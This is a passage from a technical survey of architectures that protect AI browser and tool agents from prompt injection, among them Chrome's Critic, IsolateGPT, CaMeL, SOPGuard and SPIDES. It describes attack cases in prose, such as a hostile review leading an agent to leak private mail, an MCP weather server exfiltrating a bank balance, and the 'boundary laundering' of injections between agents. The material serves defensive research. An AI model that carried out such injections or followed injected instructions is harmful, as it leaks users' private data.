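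Hiding the page from the Critic removes the attacker's direct route to it. An attacker who posts a review at Shop A has to mislead the planning model into proposing an action that the Critic will also accept. If the planning model proposes a bank transfer, the Critic can reject it as unrelated to comparing laptops, without having read the review's attempt to justify it. The Critic's task is also simpler than the planning model's, since it only has to approve or reject actions. The classifiers that Nasr and colleagues defeated all read the attacker's text, so those results do not transfer directly to the Critic. Parker gives no success rate for attacks on it.

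The attacker can still reach the Critic indirectly, because the planning model chooses the action that the metadata describes. At Shop A, entering the delivery address and entering a private message are the same type of action on the same form. The Critic can distinguish them only if the metadata includes the text to be entered, but a misled planning model can then use that text to pass the attacker's words to the Critic. Web addresses and search queries create the same problem. The host could instead pass on only a short description of the text, such as its length, but the Critic would then have less information about what it was approving.

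An attacker can also try to cause harm through an action that fits the user's task. If the user had asked the agent to buy a laptop, a hostile review might steer it to an overpriced one, and the metadata would show an ordinary purchase. Feedback after a veto may also help the attacker, because a misled planning model could use it to find an action that passes.

Chrome uses other safeguards besides the Critic. Ordinary code checks sites against a list of sensitive ones, such as banks, and requires the user's confirmation before the agent visits them. Code also restricts the web addresses that the model generates to known public ones, so the model cannot hide private data in them. The model has no direct access to saved passwords, and Chrome separately limits which sites the agent may use.

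### Judging intent and enforcing policy

A good argument for having something like the Critic is that only a model can judge whether an action fits what the user wanted. Code can establish that a form belongs to Shop A, but it cannot infer from a request to compare prices that the shop needs only an address from the mailbox. Rules written in advance will not cover every task, and asking the user about every step would defeat the purpose of having an agent.

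Iqbal argues that security cannot rest on a model's judgement, but accepts that code cannot determine the user's intent from a page. Iqbal's system, INTACT, shows the model one page element at a time, and its code permits only actions that the element supports. It asks the user first if the element comes from a third party. In tests on 1,091 real web pages, 12.8% of attacks got past INTACT's planning model, compared with 73.1% for a conventional one. The attacks that got past INTACT's model could at most trigger a request for the user's consent.

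Anderson's design separates judging intent from enforcing a policy. An outside authority decides what each user may access, and the monitor applies that decision. In an agent host, a model can propose what the task requires, the user can approve or correct the proposal, and code outside the model then enforces the resulting policy.

If the model proposes limits from the user's request alone, before the agent opens any page, a reviewer cannot influence them. An attacker who later fools the model can expand what the agent is allowed to do if the model's approval adds permissions, but still faces the code's restrictions if the model can only veto actions that the code would allow. Chrome uses models in both ways, since the Critic vetoes actions and a variant of it decides whether the agent may open a new site.

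Lan and Kaul built a system that divides the work this way. A model looks for signs of manipulation, and then code called the Origin Guard checks each request. The destination must be on a list of trusted sites, and the type of request must suit the task, so the agent cannot delete anything during a task that only involves reading. In tests with 1,000 hostile samples, fixed attacks succeeded 0.88% of the time and adaptive attacks 0.67%. An adaptive attacker could always fall back on the fixed attacks, so the lower figure suggests the adaptive test was not very demanding.

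The Guard's rules apply even when those attacks have completely misled the model. The Guard blocks any request it intercepts to an unlisted site. However, the prototype intercepts only two of the functions that scripts use to send requests. Browsers can also send data by submitting a form or loading an image, and a monitor that always runs would have to cover those routes too.

A list of trusted sites would not prevent the theft at Shop A, because the task requires Shop A to be on the list. The host needs a narrower rule. The host could show the user the delivery address the model found in the mail, ask for approval, and then let the agent enter only that exact text in the shops' address fields. The user needs to approve the address because a stranger could have sent a false one. The search box would need its own rule, since the agent could put private text there too.

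Comparing two pieces of text is simple enough for developers to test thoroughly, and no review can change how that check works. But the review could still lead the model to record the wrong price for Shop B. The agent has to write its price comparison in the notes application, so an access rule would allow the false entry along with the correct ones.

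## Separate processes for websites, separate contexts for models

The checks described so far run after a model has read hostile text and proposed an action. A host can also limit what each model reads. If a model has no private data in its context, an attacker gains little by misleading it with a hostile page. Chrome introduced a similar limit in 2018, when it stopped loading pages from different websites into the same process.

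### Site isolation in Chrome

The browser sandboxes of the late 2000s protected the user's computer from web pages, but they did less to protect web pages from each other. Although browsers split tabs among several renderer processes, a hostile page could bring another site into its own process by embedding it in a frame or opening it in a pop-up window. Code inside the shared renderer then had to keep the two sites apart, even though the sandbox's designers assumed that attackers would sometimes take over a renderer. *Site Isolation* (Reis, Moshchuk and Oskov, 2019) describes how Google addressed this problem.

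An attacker who exploits a bug in the renderer can run any code there and read everything in the process's memory. The attacker can also send false messages to the main browser process, for example to request a bank's cookies for another site's page.

Spectre attacks only read memory, but they need no bug in the browser. Processors save time by executing some instructions before it is clear whether the program needs them. They discard any unneeded results, but the work leaves traces in the processor's cache, a small, fast memory. A script can recover data from these traces by timing its own memory accesses. Browser makers tried making clocks less precise and changing how browsers compile scripts. Reis and colleagues explain that attackers can build other clocks, and that compilers cannot reliably block every variant of the attack.

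Site isolation assumes that a page may read all the memory of its process, so it keeps other sites' private data out of that process. The main browser process determines each document's site from its address and loads the document in a renderer locked to that site. A frame from another site gets a different renderer. The surrounding page can send messages to the frame through a stand-in, but the frame's contents are never in the page's memory.

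Because of the lock, the browser process also refuses a renderer's requests for another site's cookies, saved passwords or stored data. A working renderer never makes such a request, so the browser can treat one as a sign of an attack and shut the renderer down.

Chrome also has to control the files that a page loads from other sites. A hostile page could give the address of the user's bank data as the source of an image. The image would not display, but the data would be in the hostile page's process, where a Spectre attack could read it. Chrome's network code therefore withholds HTML, JSON and XML responses from other sites, since these formats often carry private data, unless the other site permits the access. Servers often label files wrongly, so the code usually checks the start of the response and blocks it only if the content matches the label. Images, video and scripts still get through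 because many pages need them.

A site is broader than an origin because it consists of only the scheme and the registered domain. `https://mail.example.com` and `https://shop.example.com` are different origins but the same site, so site isolation does not protect them from each other.

According to Chromium's *Site Isolation Design Document*, Chrome 67 introduced site isolation for all sites on desktop, and Chrome 77 introduced it on Android for sites where users log in. In the six months before the desktop launch, Chrome received nine reports of bugs that bypassed the same-origin policy. In the six months after, it received two, and site isolation contained both bugs. These numbers are small, but Reis and colleagues also found 94 earlier bugs of this kind, from 2014 to 2018, that the design would mitigate.

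### Separate servers with a shared context

In an agent host, the counterpart of a browser's renderer process is a model instance, a run of the model with its own context. An instance that never receives a source's content cannot leak that content, and text in the source cannot steer it. Two instances can share the same weights because the weights do not change while the model runs. But the host must not let content pass between them unchecked, for example through shared memory.

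*Isolation as a First-Class Principle for LLM-Agent System Safety* (Jing, Hu and colleagues, 2026) argues that prompt injection, tool misuse and memory poisoning often have the same cause, a loss of isolation at some boundary in the system. The survey organises existing research around this idea but does not test it.

Hosts that use the Model Context Protocol (MCP) already have some isolation between servers, but the servers still share the model's context. Servers can run as separate processes or on different machines, and the protocol's July 28, 2026 revision (Model Context Protocol, 2026) includes the principle that they should not "see into" one another. But if the host gives one model the outputs of all its servers, the result resembles a browser that loads every site in one renderer.

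In *Trivial Trojans*, Croce and South (2025) used this shared context to steal a bank balance. They connected the Claude Desktop application to two MCP servers, one for a real Monzo bank account and one for weather forecasts. The weather server was a published example to which they had added fewer than 25 lines. When the user asked for a forecast, this server supplied instructions that presented the bank balance as useful for personalised weather advice. The model requested the balance from the bank's server, then passed it to a tool on the weather server, which sent it to an outside address.

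The two servers never communicated directly, so the separation between them worked as designed. Claude Desktop asked the user to approve each tool call, including the one that sent the balance out. The user was one of the researchers, and the demonstration assumes that a real user would also approve. It shows how the data could get out, but not how many people would notice something wrong. The protocol only recommends such approvals, and Majeed and colleagues found that most MCP applications on GitHub do not require them.

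### IsolateGPT

Wu, Roesner and colleagues (2024) built *IsolateGPT*, a host that gives each application its own model instance, memory and operating-system process. They took process isolation from systems such as Chrome. A central hub receives the user's requests and passes messages between applications. Ordinary code handles the messages, so a prompt injection cannot make it deliver them elsewhere.

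Suppose the user asks the host to email a colleague an annual report stored in a cloud drive:

1. A planning model in the hub chooses the email application for the task and notes that it will need help from the cloud drive.
2. With the user's permission, the hub starts the email application's instance and gives it the request and any necessary data.
3. The email instance finds that it needs a file. Its message-handling code asks the hub for that function, without knowing which application provides it.
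4. The hub supplies a fixed format for the message and, if the user agrees, passes the request to the cloud drive's instance.
5. The cloud drive's instance retrieves the file, and the hub returns it to the email instance, again with the user's consent.
6. The host asks the user for approval before the email application sends the message.

A hostile email can still mislead the email instance. But that instance has no direct access to the drive, so it has to ask the hub for other documents. The hub compares each request with its original plan and warns the user if the plan did not include it.

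Wu and colleagues tested IsolateGPT and a similar host without isolation, both using GPT-4, against 1,598 attacks. Without isolation, 20.2% of the attacks succeeded. With IsolateGPT, 7.6% got as far as a permission request, which always carried a warning. The two percentages measure different things, because an attack that leads to a permission request succeeds only if the user agrees, and the test did not measure how often users would.

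The hub is a weak point because it also contains models. In *ACE*, Li, Mallick and colleagues (2025) attacked IsolateGPT using two ride-hailing applications, one of them hostile. The user wanted to compare fares. The hostile application returned text that its own model instance repeated word for word. The text then entered the context of a model in the hub, which reported an inflated fare for the competitor. In another attack, the hostile application's output made the hub stop before it called the competitor.

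Wu and colleagues tested a similar manipulation of fares and found that IsolateGPT prevented it. In their test, a new model instance with no application of its own combined the two results. One model must still read both outputs to compare them, which ends the isolation unless the outputs are limited to something like a number.

Li and colleagues also manipulated the hub through an application's description, which led the planning model to leave out a competing application before any application had run. Their system, ACE, plans in two stages to prevent this. A model first writes a plan from the user's request alone, using generic functions such as "load a document". The host then matches each function to an installed application, considering each candidate separately so that one description cannot affect whether another is chosen. Li and colleagues report that ACE stopped their new attacks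 and all those in InjecAgent, a standard benchmark.

### The dual-model pattern

IsolateGPT divides the work by application, so the instance that reads an email can also use the email tools. In *The Dual LLM pattern for building AI assistants*, Willison (2023) proposed dividing it by trust instead. A privileged model reads the user's request and can use tools, but it never reads untrusted content, which goes to a quarantined model that has no tools. A controller, which is ordinary code, runs the tools and stores the results.

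If the user asks for a summary of the latest email, the privileged model sends the controller a command to fetch the email. The controller stores the email under a name such as `$VAR1` and gives the privileged model only the name. The privileged model then requests a summary of `$VAR1`. The controller passes the text to the quarantined model, stores the summary as `$VAR2` and displays it to the user at the privileged model's request. The variable names work somewhat like Chrome's stand-ins for frames, since they let the privileged model refer to content outside its context.

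An injection in the email can corrupt the summary but cannot make the privileged model delete the mailbox. Willison allows the quarantined model's output to reach the privileged model only when it is a choice from a fixed list of categories, because the controller can check that the answer is on the list before passing it on.

Willison proposed the pattern without publishing attack tests, and called it "pretty bad" because of the work and inconvenience it adds. A single programming error that passes untrusted text to the privileged model would defeat the design. The displayed summary can also contain a message that tricks the user into copying private data to a hostile site.

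### CaMeL

Two years later, researchers at Google DeepMind pointed out another weakness in the dual-model pattern. Suppose the user asks the agent to send Bob a document and says that Bob's address is in the meeting notes. The quarantined model has to extract the address, so an attacker who can edit the notes can make it return their own address instead. The privileged model, which receives only a variable name, then sends the document to the attacker.

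Their system, CaMeL, limits this by checking where values come from. Willison (2025) explains it in *CaMeL offers a promising new direction for mitigating prompt injection attacks*, with a request to find Bob's address in the last email and send him a reminder about a meeting:

1. The privileged model reads the request and writes a short program that fetches the email, extracts the address and sends the reminder.
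2. An interpreter runs the program. When it reaches the extraction step, it gives the email to the quarantined model and accepts only an answer in the form of an email address.
3. The interpreter records that the address came from the email, which makes it untrusted.
4. Before sending the reminder, the interpreter applies a policy. If the user already trusts the address, it sends the message. Otherwise, it can ask for approval.

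The program fixes the control flow (which tools may run and in what order) before any model reads the email. An attacker who misleads the quarantined model can change a value in the program but cannot add a step. The policies guard against changed values. CaMeL uses the term "capabilities" for its records of where data came from and who may read it, but these are labels, unlike the capabilities that Hardy proposed.

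According to *Open Challenges in Multi-Agent Security* (2025), CaMeL stopped nearly all attacks in AgentDojo, a benchmark of office, banking and travel tasks. In *Can CaMeLs Talk?*, Peters-Gill, Semler and colleagues (2026) tested whether this protection holds when several agents work together. They found a gap when testing three agents that all used CaMeL: a coordinator, one that reads a database and one that sends notifications.

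The user asked the system to send a colleague a summary of job applicants from a database that contained a prompt injection. The coordinator correctly treated the database's content as untrusted data, but then put the summary in a written message to the notification agent. That agent treated the whole message as its user's request, so its privileged model read the injection and added a step that emailed the summary to an outsider. Peters-Gill and colleagues call this boundary laundering.

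They closed the gap by giving agents one channel for instructions and another for data. The interpreter rejects any instruction that depends on a tool's output, and the receiving agent's privileged model cannot read anything in the data channel. The table shows the share of attacks that succeeded in a multi-agent version of AgentDojo, with 949 attacks for each model and setting.

| Model | Without CaMeL | CaMeL in each agent | CaMeL with separate channels |
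|---|---|---|---|
| GPT-4.1 | 36.1% | 0.5% | 0.0% |
| Gemini 2.5 Pro | 24.6% | 0.4% | 0.0% |
| Gemini 2.5 Flash Lite | 2.1% | 0.0% | 0.0% |
| Claude Fable 5 | 1.5% | 0.0% | 0.0% |
| GPT-5.5 | 0.0% | 0.0% | 0.0% |
| Average | 12.9% | 0.2% | 0.0% |

The average without CaMeL comes mostly from two older models. GPT-5.5 resisted every attack unaided, so this benchmark cannot show whether CaMeL makes that model safer. Peters-Gill and colleagues warn that stronger, adaptive attacks might still succeed against GPT-5.5. CaMeL's structure is the better reason to expect it to resist new attacks, because untrusted text cannot add a step to the program, however it is worded. The researchers ran these tests without security policies, so the results provide little evidence about attacks that only change a value.

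### Tasks that combine sources

For the laptop-shopping task, a host could use one quarantined instance for each shop and another for the mail. The shop instances would return only prices, and the mail instance only an address. Ordinary code would then compare the offers and fill in the forms. The reviewer at Shop A could no longer steal a private message, because no instance would have access to both the review and the mail.

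The reviewer could not change Shop B's price either, as long as the host gives each shop's page to a separate quarantined instance. If the host gave both pages to one instance and asked which offer was better, the review could affect the answer about both shops, even though the instance has no tools.

The task still needs channels for the prices and the address, and false values can pass through them. The review could lead the first instance to return the wrong price for Shop A. Checking the format would not help, because a wrong price is still a valid number and contains no instruction. A stranger's email could also lead the mail instance to return a false address, or private text in place of an address. CaMeL would record that the value came from the mail, but this would not distinguish it from the real address, which also comes from the mail.

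A false value can also determine which of the planned steps the host takes. Peters-Gill and colleagues call this branch steering. If the user asked the agent to buy from the cheaper shop, a false price could send the order to the wrong shop without adding anything to the program.

Other tasks are hard to plan before reading the content. If a user asks an agent to do whatever an email requests, a planner that cannot read the email cannot identify the tools it will need. CaMeL's planner also has to write code for results it has not seen, so Peters-Gill and colleagues added a full description of the output format to every tool. An ordinary shop page has no such description, so a planner that cannot see the page may be unable to choose the right button. In tests, CaMeL also failed to complete some harmless tasks.

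### Isolation in 2026 hosts

Pirch and colleagues examined four open-source agents in 2026: OpenClaw, the security-focused IronClaw, the deliberately small Nanobot, and NemoClaw, which runs an existing agent inside a protective layer. They found "no deliberate isolation policy" for the context in any of them. Tools that ran one after another put their results in the same context, so one tool's output could influence how the agent used the next. Agents sometimes summarised a long context to save space, which could incidentally remove some material.

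Some of these agents do confine their tools' code. IronClaw runs many tools, but not those on MCP servers, in a restricted environment with a list of permitted web addresses. NemoClaw puts the whole agent in a sandbox. These agents are roughly where browsers were before site isolation, with some protection for the computer but little separation between sources. Pirch and colleagues think hosts could go further by giving each tool call a context with only the data it needs. Their study covers popular agents that users run and extend themselves, but not coding agents or hosted services.

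Chrome isolates one of its models, the User Alignment Critic, which Google Cloud describes as partly inspired by CaMeL. In guidance for developers, Google (2026) describes similar critics for agents that use tools offered by web pages.

Chrome's planning model is exposed to web content, and Parker acknowledges that this makes it inherently vulnerable to prompt injection. In CaMeL, by contrast, the model that chooses the steps has not read any untrusted content.

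## Attaching origin labels to what the agent has read

Isolation keeps private data away from any model that reads hostile text, which is awkward when a task needs both. A host can instead let one model read everything, as most hosts already do, and record where the material came from. Before the agent sends anything, the host compares this record with the destination. This is a form of information-flow control, which labels data by source and permitted readers and checks the labels whenever a program uses or sends the data. Some early browsers tried another form, called taint tracking.

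With labels, the host doesn't have to recognise an attack. Wang and colleagues tested five detectors that look for injected text in web pages, and none had both few misses and few false alarms. The detector WebSentinel missed at most 1% of the hostile pages on any of the five sinks, but flagged 6% to 44% of the clean ones.

### Trail of Bits' extended same-origin rule

The extension of the same-origin policy that Trail of Bits proposed in January 2026 needs only a list. The host adds the origin of every page that a tool loads, along with every attachment, to a list for the chat session. Each file counts as a separate origin. The list then determines which requests the agent may make:

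- If the list is empty, the agent may make requests freely.
- If the list has one origin, the agent may make requests only to that origin.
- If the list has several origins, the agent may make no requests.

Trail of Bits blocks all requests in the last case because there is no way to tell which origin influenced the model's output. A request to one site might contain data from another, or a third site's text might have prompted it. Trail of Bits would allow web search only while the list is empty, because search results come from many sources and search queries can carry data out.

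In the laptop-shopping task, the list starts empty, so the agent can open Shop A. It can then search the shop and read the reviews, since those requests go to the one listed origin. The task stops when the agent tries to open Shop B, a second origin, so the agent never reaches the delivery address.

A different order would not help. If the agent read the mail first, it could not open either shop. If it began with a web search, the results would add several origins to the list, and the agent could not open any of them. The user could run a separate chat for each shop and carry the prices and the address across by hand, but the agent was supposed to save the user that work.

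The rule's main strength is that ordinary code can enforce it, so no injection can shorten the list. The host would have to apply the rule to redirects too, since Comet's auditors reached Gmail through one. The rule doesn't cover the user's own messages, because they have no origin. If a hostile page is the only entry on the list, the agent may still send that page's server anything the user has typed in the chat.

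Trail of Bits offers the rule as a direction for further research, without an implementation or test results, and suggests CaMeL as another option.

### How SOPGuard works

Wang and colleagues built a more permissive system, SOPGuard, into BrowserOS. It labels individual pieces of text instead of the whole session, and it asks the user instead of blocking. It works in four steps:

1. **Reading.** When the agent calls a tool that reads a page, SOPGuard stores the result in a database with the page's origin.
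2. **Propagation.** When the model writes a response, SOPGuard identifies any new data in it that derives from earlier entries. It stores each new item with the origins of all the entries it depends on.
3. **Checking.** When the agent calls a tool that writes text into a page, SOPGuard looks up the text's origins and compares them with the page's origin.
4. **Asking.** If any of the text's origins differs from the page's, SOPGuard holds the write and shows a pop-up that names the origins. The agent can continue only if the user approves.

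If O(x) is the set of origins for a text x, and o(w) is the origin of a page w, the agent can write x to w without confirmation only when O(x) contains no origin other than o(w). An empty set also passes, so the agent can freely type the user's own words.

SOPGuard labels what the agent reads through the browser's tools, so the shopping example works only if the mail and the notes are web pages too. The database might then contain these entries:

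| Entry | Text | Origins | Depends on |
|---|---|---|---|
| 1 | Shop A's page | Shop A | – |
| 2 | Shop B's page | Shop B | – |
| 3 | A message that mentions the delivery address | Mail | – |
| 4 | The delivery address | Mail | 3 |
| 5 | The price comparison | Shop A, Shop B | 1, 2 |

The agent can open both shops and the mailbox without interruption, because opening a page is not a write. SOPGuard prompts the user when the agent enters the address at Shop A, again when it does so at Shop B, and again when it saves the comparison in the notes. It also prompts the user if a review at Shop A leads the agent to enter a private message in the shop's form.

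### Who decides where a paraphrase came from

Code can label a page when the agent reads it, but matching text may not reveal the source of a summary or a calculated average, which may share no words with the original. SOPGuard uses the agent's own model to identify the sources of such data. After each response, it gives the model the user's prompt, the response and the label database, and asks which entries the new data derives from. Code then combines the origins of those entries. When checking outgoing text, SOPGuard first looks for it in the database and asks the model only if it finds no match.

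The final comparison is therefore deterministic, but some of the labels it uses come from a model that reads the attacker's text. This brings back the weakness of using a model as the reference monitor, in a narrower form. If the model wrongly attributes a private message to Shop A, the origins match and SOPGuard never asks the user. SOPGuard also instructs the model to prefer the smallest set of entries that supports the new data, which reduces false alarms but may make the model more likely to omit a relevant entry.

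Some omissions make no difference. For example, if a text comes from both the mail and Shop B but the model lists only Shop B, SOPGuard will still ask before the agent writes the text at Shop A.

To measure accuracy, Wang and colleagues had the agent read pages from two to ten origins and derive a series of results from them. They compared the model's labels with those of human annotators using the Jaccard coefficient, which divides the number of origins that appear in both sets by the number that appear in at least one. If the true sources are the mail and Shop A, and the model names only Shop A, the score is 0.5. GPT-5.4 and OpenAI's o3 averaged at least 0.955 for every number of origins tested. The smaller GPT-5.4-mini stayed above 0.9 with up to eight origins. These scores don't distinguish missing labels from extra ones, although only missing labels can let data leak unnoticed.

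The researchers also attacked the labelling directly, with injections meant to convince the model that the outgoing text came only from the destination page. In 100 sampled cases, handwritten attacks hardly raised the violation rate. Automatically optimised attacks raised it slightly but needed many more attempts. To succeed, an attack must make the agent both leak the data and mislabel it, and it fails if the database already contains the text with its correct origin. Wang and colleagues accept that stronger attacks may exist.

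### What a violation rate of zero covers

On SOPBench, SOPGuard reduced BrowserOS's violation rate to 0.00, both with and without an attacker. This is a strong result for the leaks that SOPBench counts, but several kinds of failure fall outside it:

- **Reworded data.** SOPBench counts only exact copies, which are also the easiest text to find in the database, so the result reveals little about leaks in paraphrased form.
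- **Other routes out.** Wang and colleagues describe the check for tools that write text into a page, such as one that fills in a field. Trail of Bits' attacks often put the data in a web address and had the agent open it.
- **Mistaken approvals.** Wang and colleagues do not consider a transfer a violation if the user approves it, so the rate does not reflect how well people answer the pop-up.

The result without an attacker, where the private data was in a frame, is also hard to interpret, because SOPGuard's labelling function, as described, returns one origin for the current page. It is unclear how the system distinguished the frame's text from the rest of the page.

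In *SPIDES*, Zverev, Kim and colleagues (2026) tested SOPGuard under much harsher conditions. Their test used a closed network of 28 websites and 56 attacks. They assumed that an attacker whose text reaches the model can choose what the model does, so for injected instructions, their software replaced the model's tool calls with the attacker's. They also assumed that the user denies every request the attacker caused. Between 53.2% and 73.2% of the attacks still succeeded, depending on the model.

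Most of that gap comes from the choice of attacks. SOPGuard only tries to stop attacks that move data between origins. Of the 56 attacks, 26 stayed within one origin, and half aimed to cause a harmful action, such as an unauthorised purchase, rather than a leak. Zverev and colleagues were testing a competitor to their own system, and a different mix of attacks would give a different percentage. The result still shows that a host with SOPGuard would need other defences.

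### Over-labelling

A host could label every output with every origin in the context, so that it doesn't have to rely on the model's account of its sources. *Securing AI Agents with Information-Flow Control* (2025) uses this method in its basic design and describes it as sound, meaning that it misses no real flow of data, but possibly too conservative. *Agent Security is a Systems Problem* (2026) argues that hosts can't currently assume that an output draws on fewer origins, because a language model mixes all its inputs.

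The drawback is that labels accumulate. Once the agent has read both shops and the mail, everything it writes carries all three origins. If it typed "laptop" into Shop A's search box, the host would treat the word as possible private mail, even though it came from the user's request. After a few more pages, almost every write would trigger a warning, and the labels would no longer help distinguish theft from an ordinary search. This method scored consistently low in Wang and colleagues' accuracy test. Trail of Bits' rule rests on the same assumption about the context, so it blocks all requests once the list has several origins.

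Dividing the work among several agents helps, since each has its own context. In *The Limits of Information-Flow Control Enforcement for Agentic Systems*, Gregory, Domico and colleagues (2026) simulated how much this can help. In their model, an agent that receives sensitive data keeps the sensitive label from then on and passes it along with its messages. They measured the share of tool calls that introduced this label or ran under it, mostly in tasks of 20 calls.

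Using more agents reduced this share, as did giving the sensitive tools to only a few of them. Letting agents communicate directly also helped. When four of the 20 calls were sensitive, routing messages through a central agent affected about 5 percentage points more of the calls. But if every agent can contact every other, five agents have 10 links to monitor and 20 agents have 190. Even the best arrangement left many calls with the sensitive label, because some steps depend on sensitive data. Gregory and colleagues conclude that hosts also need declassification, a controlled way to remove labels. The simulation involved no language model, so it shows how labels spread under fixed rules, not how often real tasks would fail.

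### More selective labels

Several research groups have tried to identify which inputs affected an output. In *Permissive Information-Flow Analysis for Large Language Models*, Siddiqui, Gaonkar and colleagues select the influential inputs and regenerate the response from those alone. This gives the shorter label a firmer basis than SOPGuard's, because the second response cannot quote text that the model did not receive. An injection could still affect which inputs are selected. In more than 85% of cases, the method produced a more permissive label than asking the model to predict one, but this figure does not measure whether the labels were correct.

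*GIF* (2026) measures how much a passage influences a model's output. It slightly alters the numbers that represent the passage inside the model and calculates how much the probabilities of possible outputs change. A host would still have to decide how much influence is enough to attach a label.

In tests, other selective methods have both missed real information flows and flagged false ones. *RTBAS* (2025) labels tool calls with categories of private information, such as credit card numbers. A model acting as judge identified the exact set of categories in 70% of calls. A method based on the model's attention, its internal weighting of the input, did so in 57.3%, barely better than the 56.7% from assuming that every call leaks everything. *Ghost in the Agent* (2026) tested a tracker called NeuroTaint on 400 scenarios. The tracker missed 13 real flows and raised 16 false alarms. Many of the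 misses involved information that had been reworded several times. Most of the false alarms involved text that only shared a topic with the source or that the model could have known anyway.

SPIDES, by Zverev and colleagues, tracks labels in code instead of relying on a model to assign them. The code keeps one label for the whole context, and that label can only become stricter. To delay this tightening, the host hides untrusted or private text behind variables, as in the dual-model pattern. The agent can ask to see a hidden value, but the context then takes on that value's label for the rest of the task. In tests, agents did this between 1.1 and 2.7 times per task on average, so hiding text often only postpones over-labelling.

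### Blocking or asking

Wang and colleagues chose to ask the user because many transfers between sites are legitimate. Their example is a user who wants the agent to send a shipping address from a shop to a trusted contact on Discord. If the user approves, the transfer is comparable to copying and pasting by hand. Blocking the transfer would end the task, as Trail of Bits' rule does at the second shop.

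Asking the user works only if they can tell a good request from a bad one, and *Agent Security is a Systems Problem* warns that people may approve a permission prompt they don't understand. SOPGuard's pop-up identifies the transfer by its origins. At Shop A, the delivery address and a stolen private message would both appear as a transfer from the mail to the shop, and the user would have good reason to approve the first. Showing the exact text would make the difference obvious in this case, but it would help less with long texts, because Trail of Bits expects that users would often accept previews of long documents without reading them.

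Users are less likely to answer approval requests carefully when many are unnecessary. In one of Zverev and colleagues' harmless tasks, the agent had to compare a discount on a deals site with the regular price on a shopping search engine. SOPGuard asked for approval in all 25 runs because the product's name had to move from one site to the other. The system in *Confuse the Model, Control the Flow* (2026) reduces such requests by recording in advance who may receive each private record. Summaries and paraphrases inherit these permissions from all their sources, and the system asks the data's owner only when the permissions don't settle the matter. At the start of the laptop task, the user could authorise both shops to receive the delivery address. The host would then need to ask only if the agent tried to send them something else from the mail.

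## When one origin holds both trusted and untrusted content

Trail of Bits' rule and SOPGuard both treat everything from one origin alike. But a single page at Shop A may contain the shop's price, a stranger's review and the user's saved card number. The origin doesn't show which of these could carry an attack or which should stay private. Zverev and colleagues, who built SPIDES, argue that restoring the same-origin policy is neither sufficient nor necessary to protect users of browser agents.

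### Two cases against relying on origins

The first case is an attack within one social network. In a direct message, an attacker tells the agent to copy the user's private recovery email address into the user's public profile. The message, the address and the profile all have the same origin, so SOPGuard finds no mismatch. In 25 runs it never prompted for approval, and the address became public every time.

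The second case is a harmless price comparison between a deals site and a shopping search engine. SOPGuard prompted for approval in every run, 33 times in total. SPIDES prompted in only four of the 25 runs, and never merely because data had crossed origins. But over the whole benchmark, SPIDES prompts more often than SOPGuard because it checks for more kinds of harm.

These cases are evidence against using origins as an agent's main policy, but not against the browser's same-origin policy. SPIDES still relies on the browser to stop a hostile frame's scripts from reading the page around it.

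### Labels on parts of a page

In SPIDES, the user keeps a list of sites whose operators they trust, and the system assumes that the user has accounts only on those sites. The operators attach two labels to the elements of their pages, such as headings, buttons and paragraphs:

- The integrity label is "trusted" if the operator can vouch for the content and "untrusted" if not, as with a customer review.
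- The reader label is the set of parties who may receive the content. It can include the user and any number of origins. A saved card number might have only the user and the shop as readers, while public content has everyone.

An unlabelled element inherits the labels of the nearest labelled element that contains it. If no labelled element contains it, SPIDES treats it as trusted and public. On sites outside the user's list, SPIDES ignores any labels and treats everything as untrusted and public.

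The context has the same two labels and starts as trusted and public. If text would make either label stricter, SPIDES hides it behind a variable, which the agent can use without seeing the text. If the agent asks to see untrusted text, the context becomes untrusted. If it asks to see private text, the context keeps only those readers who are also allowed to read that text.

SPIDES then applies two policies to the agent's actions:

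- **Trusted action** holds if neither the context nor the data in the action contains anything untrusted.
- **Permitted flow** holds if the destination is an authorised reader of both the context and the data. For a destination o, this means that o must belong to R(context) ∩ R(data), where R is the set of readers.

| What the agent does | What SPIDES requires |
|---|---|
| Reads a page | Nothing |
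| Fills in a field without submitting it | Trusted action or permitted flow |
| Clicks, opens an address or submits a form on a trusted site | Trusted action |
| Clicks, opens an address or submits a form on any other site | Trusted action or permitted flow |
| Runs its own code in the browser | Always blocked |

If an action other than running code fails its test, SPIDES asks the user. The rule for clicks is strict because one tool handles every click, and the host can't predict whether a click will follow a link or delete an account. So SPIDES treats any click on a trusted site as one that may use the user's account.

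The rule for filling in fields is looser. If nothing untrusted has influenced the agent, it may type private data into any site, even one that is not an authorised reader. This allows many ordinary tasks, but it means SPIDES protects against attackers more than against the model's own mistakes.

### Reader sets in the shopping task

Suppose the user trusts both shops and the mail service, and gives the agent the delivery address in a labelled note. SPIDES accepts such notes alongside the request. The labels might be:

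| Content | Integrity | Readers |
|---|---|---|
| Laptop price at Shop A | Trusted | Everyone |
| Customer review at Shop A | Untrusted | Everyone |
| Delivery address in the user's note | Trusted | User, Shop A, Shop B |
| Private message in the mailbox | Untrusted | User, mail service |

The agent opens the mailbox and then Shop A. It can see the price, but the review, the address and the message are hidden behind variables. The reviewer's instructions have no effect because the model hasn't read them.

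Now suppose the user wants to know what customers think of the keyboard, so the agent asks to see the review. The context becomes untrusted, but its readers still include everyone. The review then leads the agent to enter the private message in Shop A's form. Trusted action fails, and so does permitted flow, because the message's readers are only the user and the mail service. SPIDES holds the action and asks the user.

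If the agent enters the delivery address instead, permitted flow holds because Shop A is among the address's readers, so the agent can fill in the field without approval. Submitting the form would still need approval because the context is untrusted and Shop A is a trusted site.

If the agent had also looked at the private message, the context's readers would have shrunk to the user and the mail service. The address and the context would then have only the user in common:

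{user, Shop A, Shop B} ∩ {user, mail service} = {user}

Even the address would now need approval at Shop A, since the agent could mix parts of the message into anything it types.

In the original task, the address is in the mailbox, so it would have the same labels as the private message. SPIDES would have to ask for permission before the agent entered the address at either shop. Reader sets avoid this request only if someone has listed the shops in advance, and a mail provider can't know where its customers will shop.

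Reader sets don't stop the profile attack either. The social network already stores the recovery address and is one of its authorised readers, so SPIDES lets the agent type the address into the profile. SPIDES does block the next step, the click on "Save changes", because the hostile message has made the context untrusted. But if the site saved each field automatically, the address could become public before that click. Zverev and colleagues acknowledge that their reader labels can't distinguish all the recipients within one origin.

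### Untrusted Content Masking

An earlier system used only integrity labels. In *Untrusted Content Masking for Web Agents with Security Guarantees* (Nikolić, Zverev and colleagues, 2026), site owners mark the regions of a page that they can't vouch for. The host covers those regions with placeholders, such as "review 3". If the agent needs information from a covered region, it asks a quarantined model, which may answer only with yes or no, a number, a date or a choice from a list.

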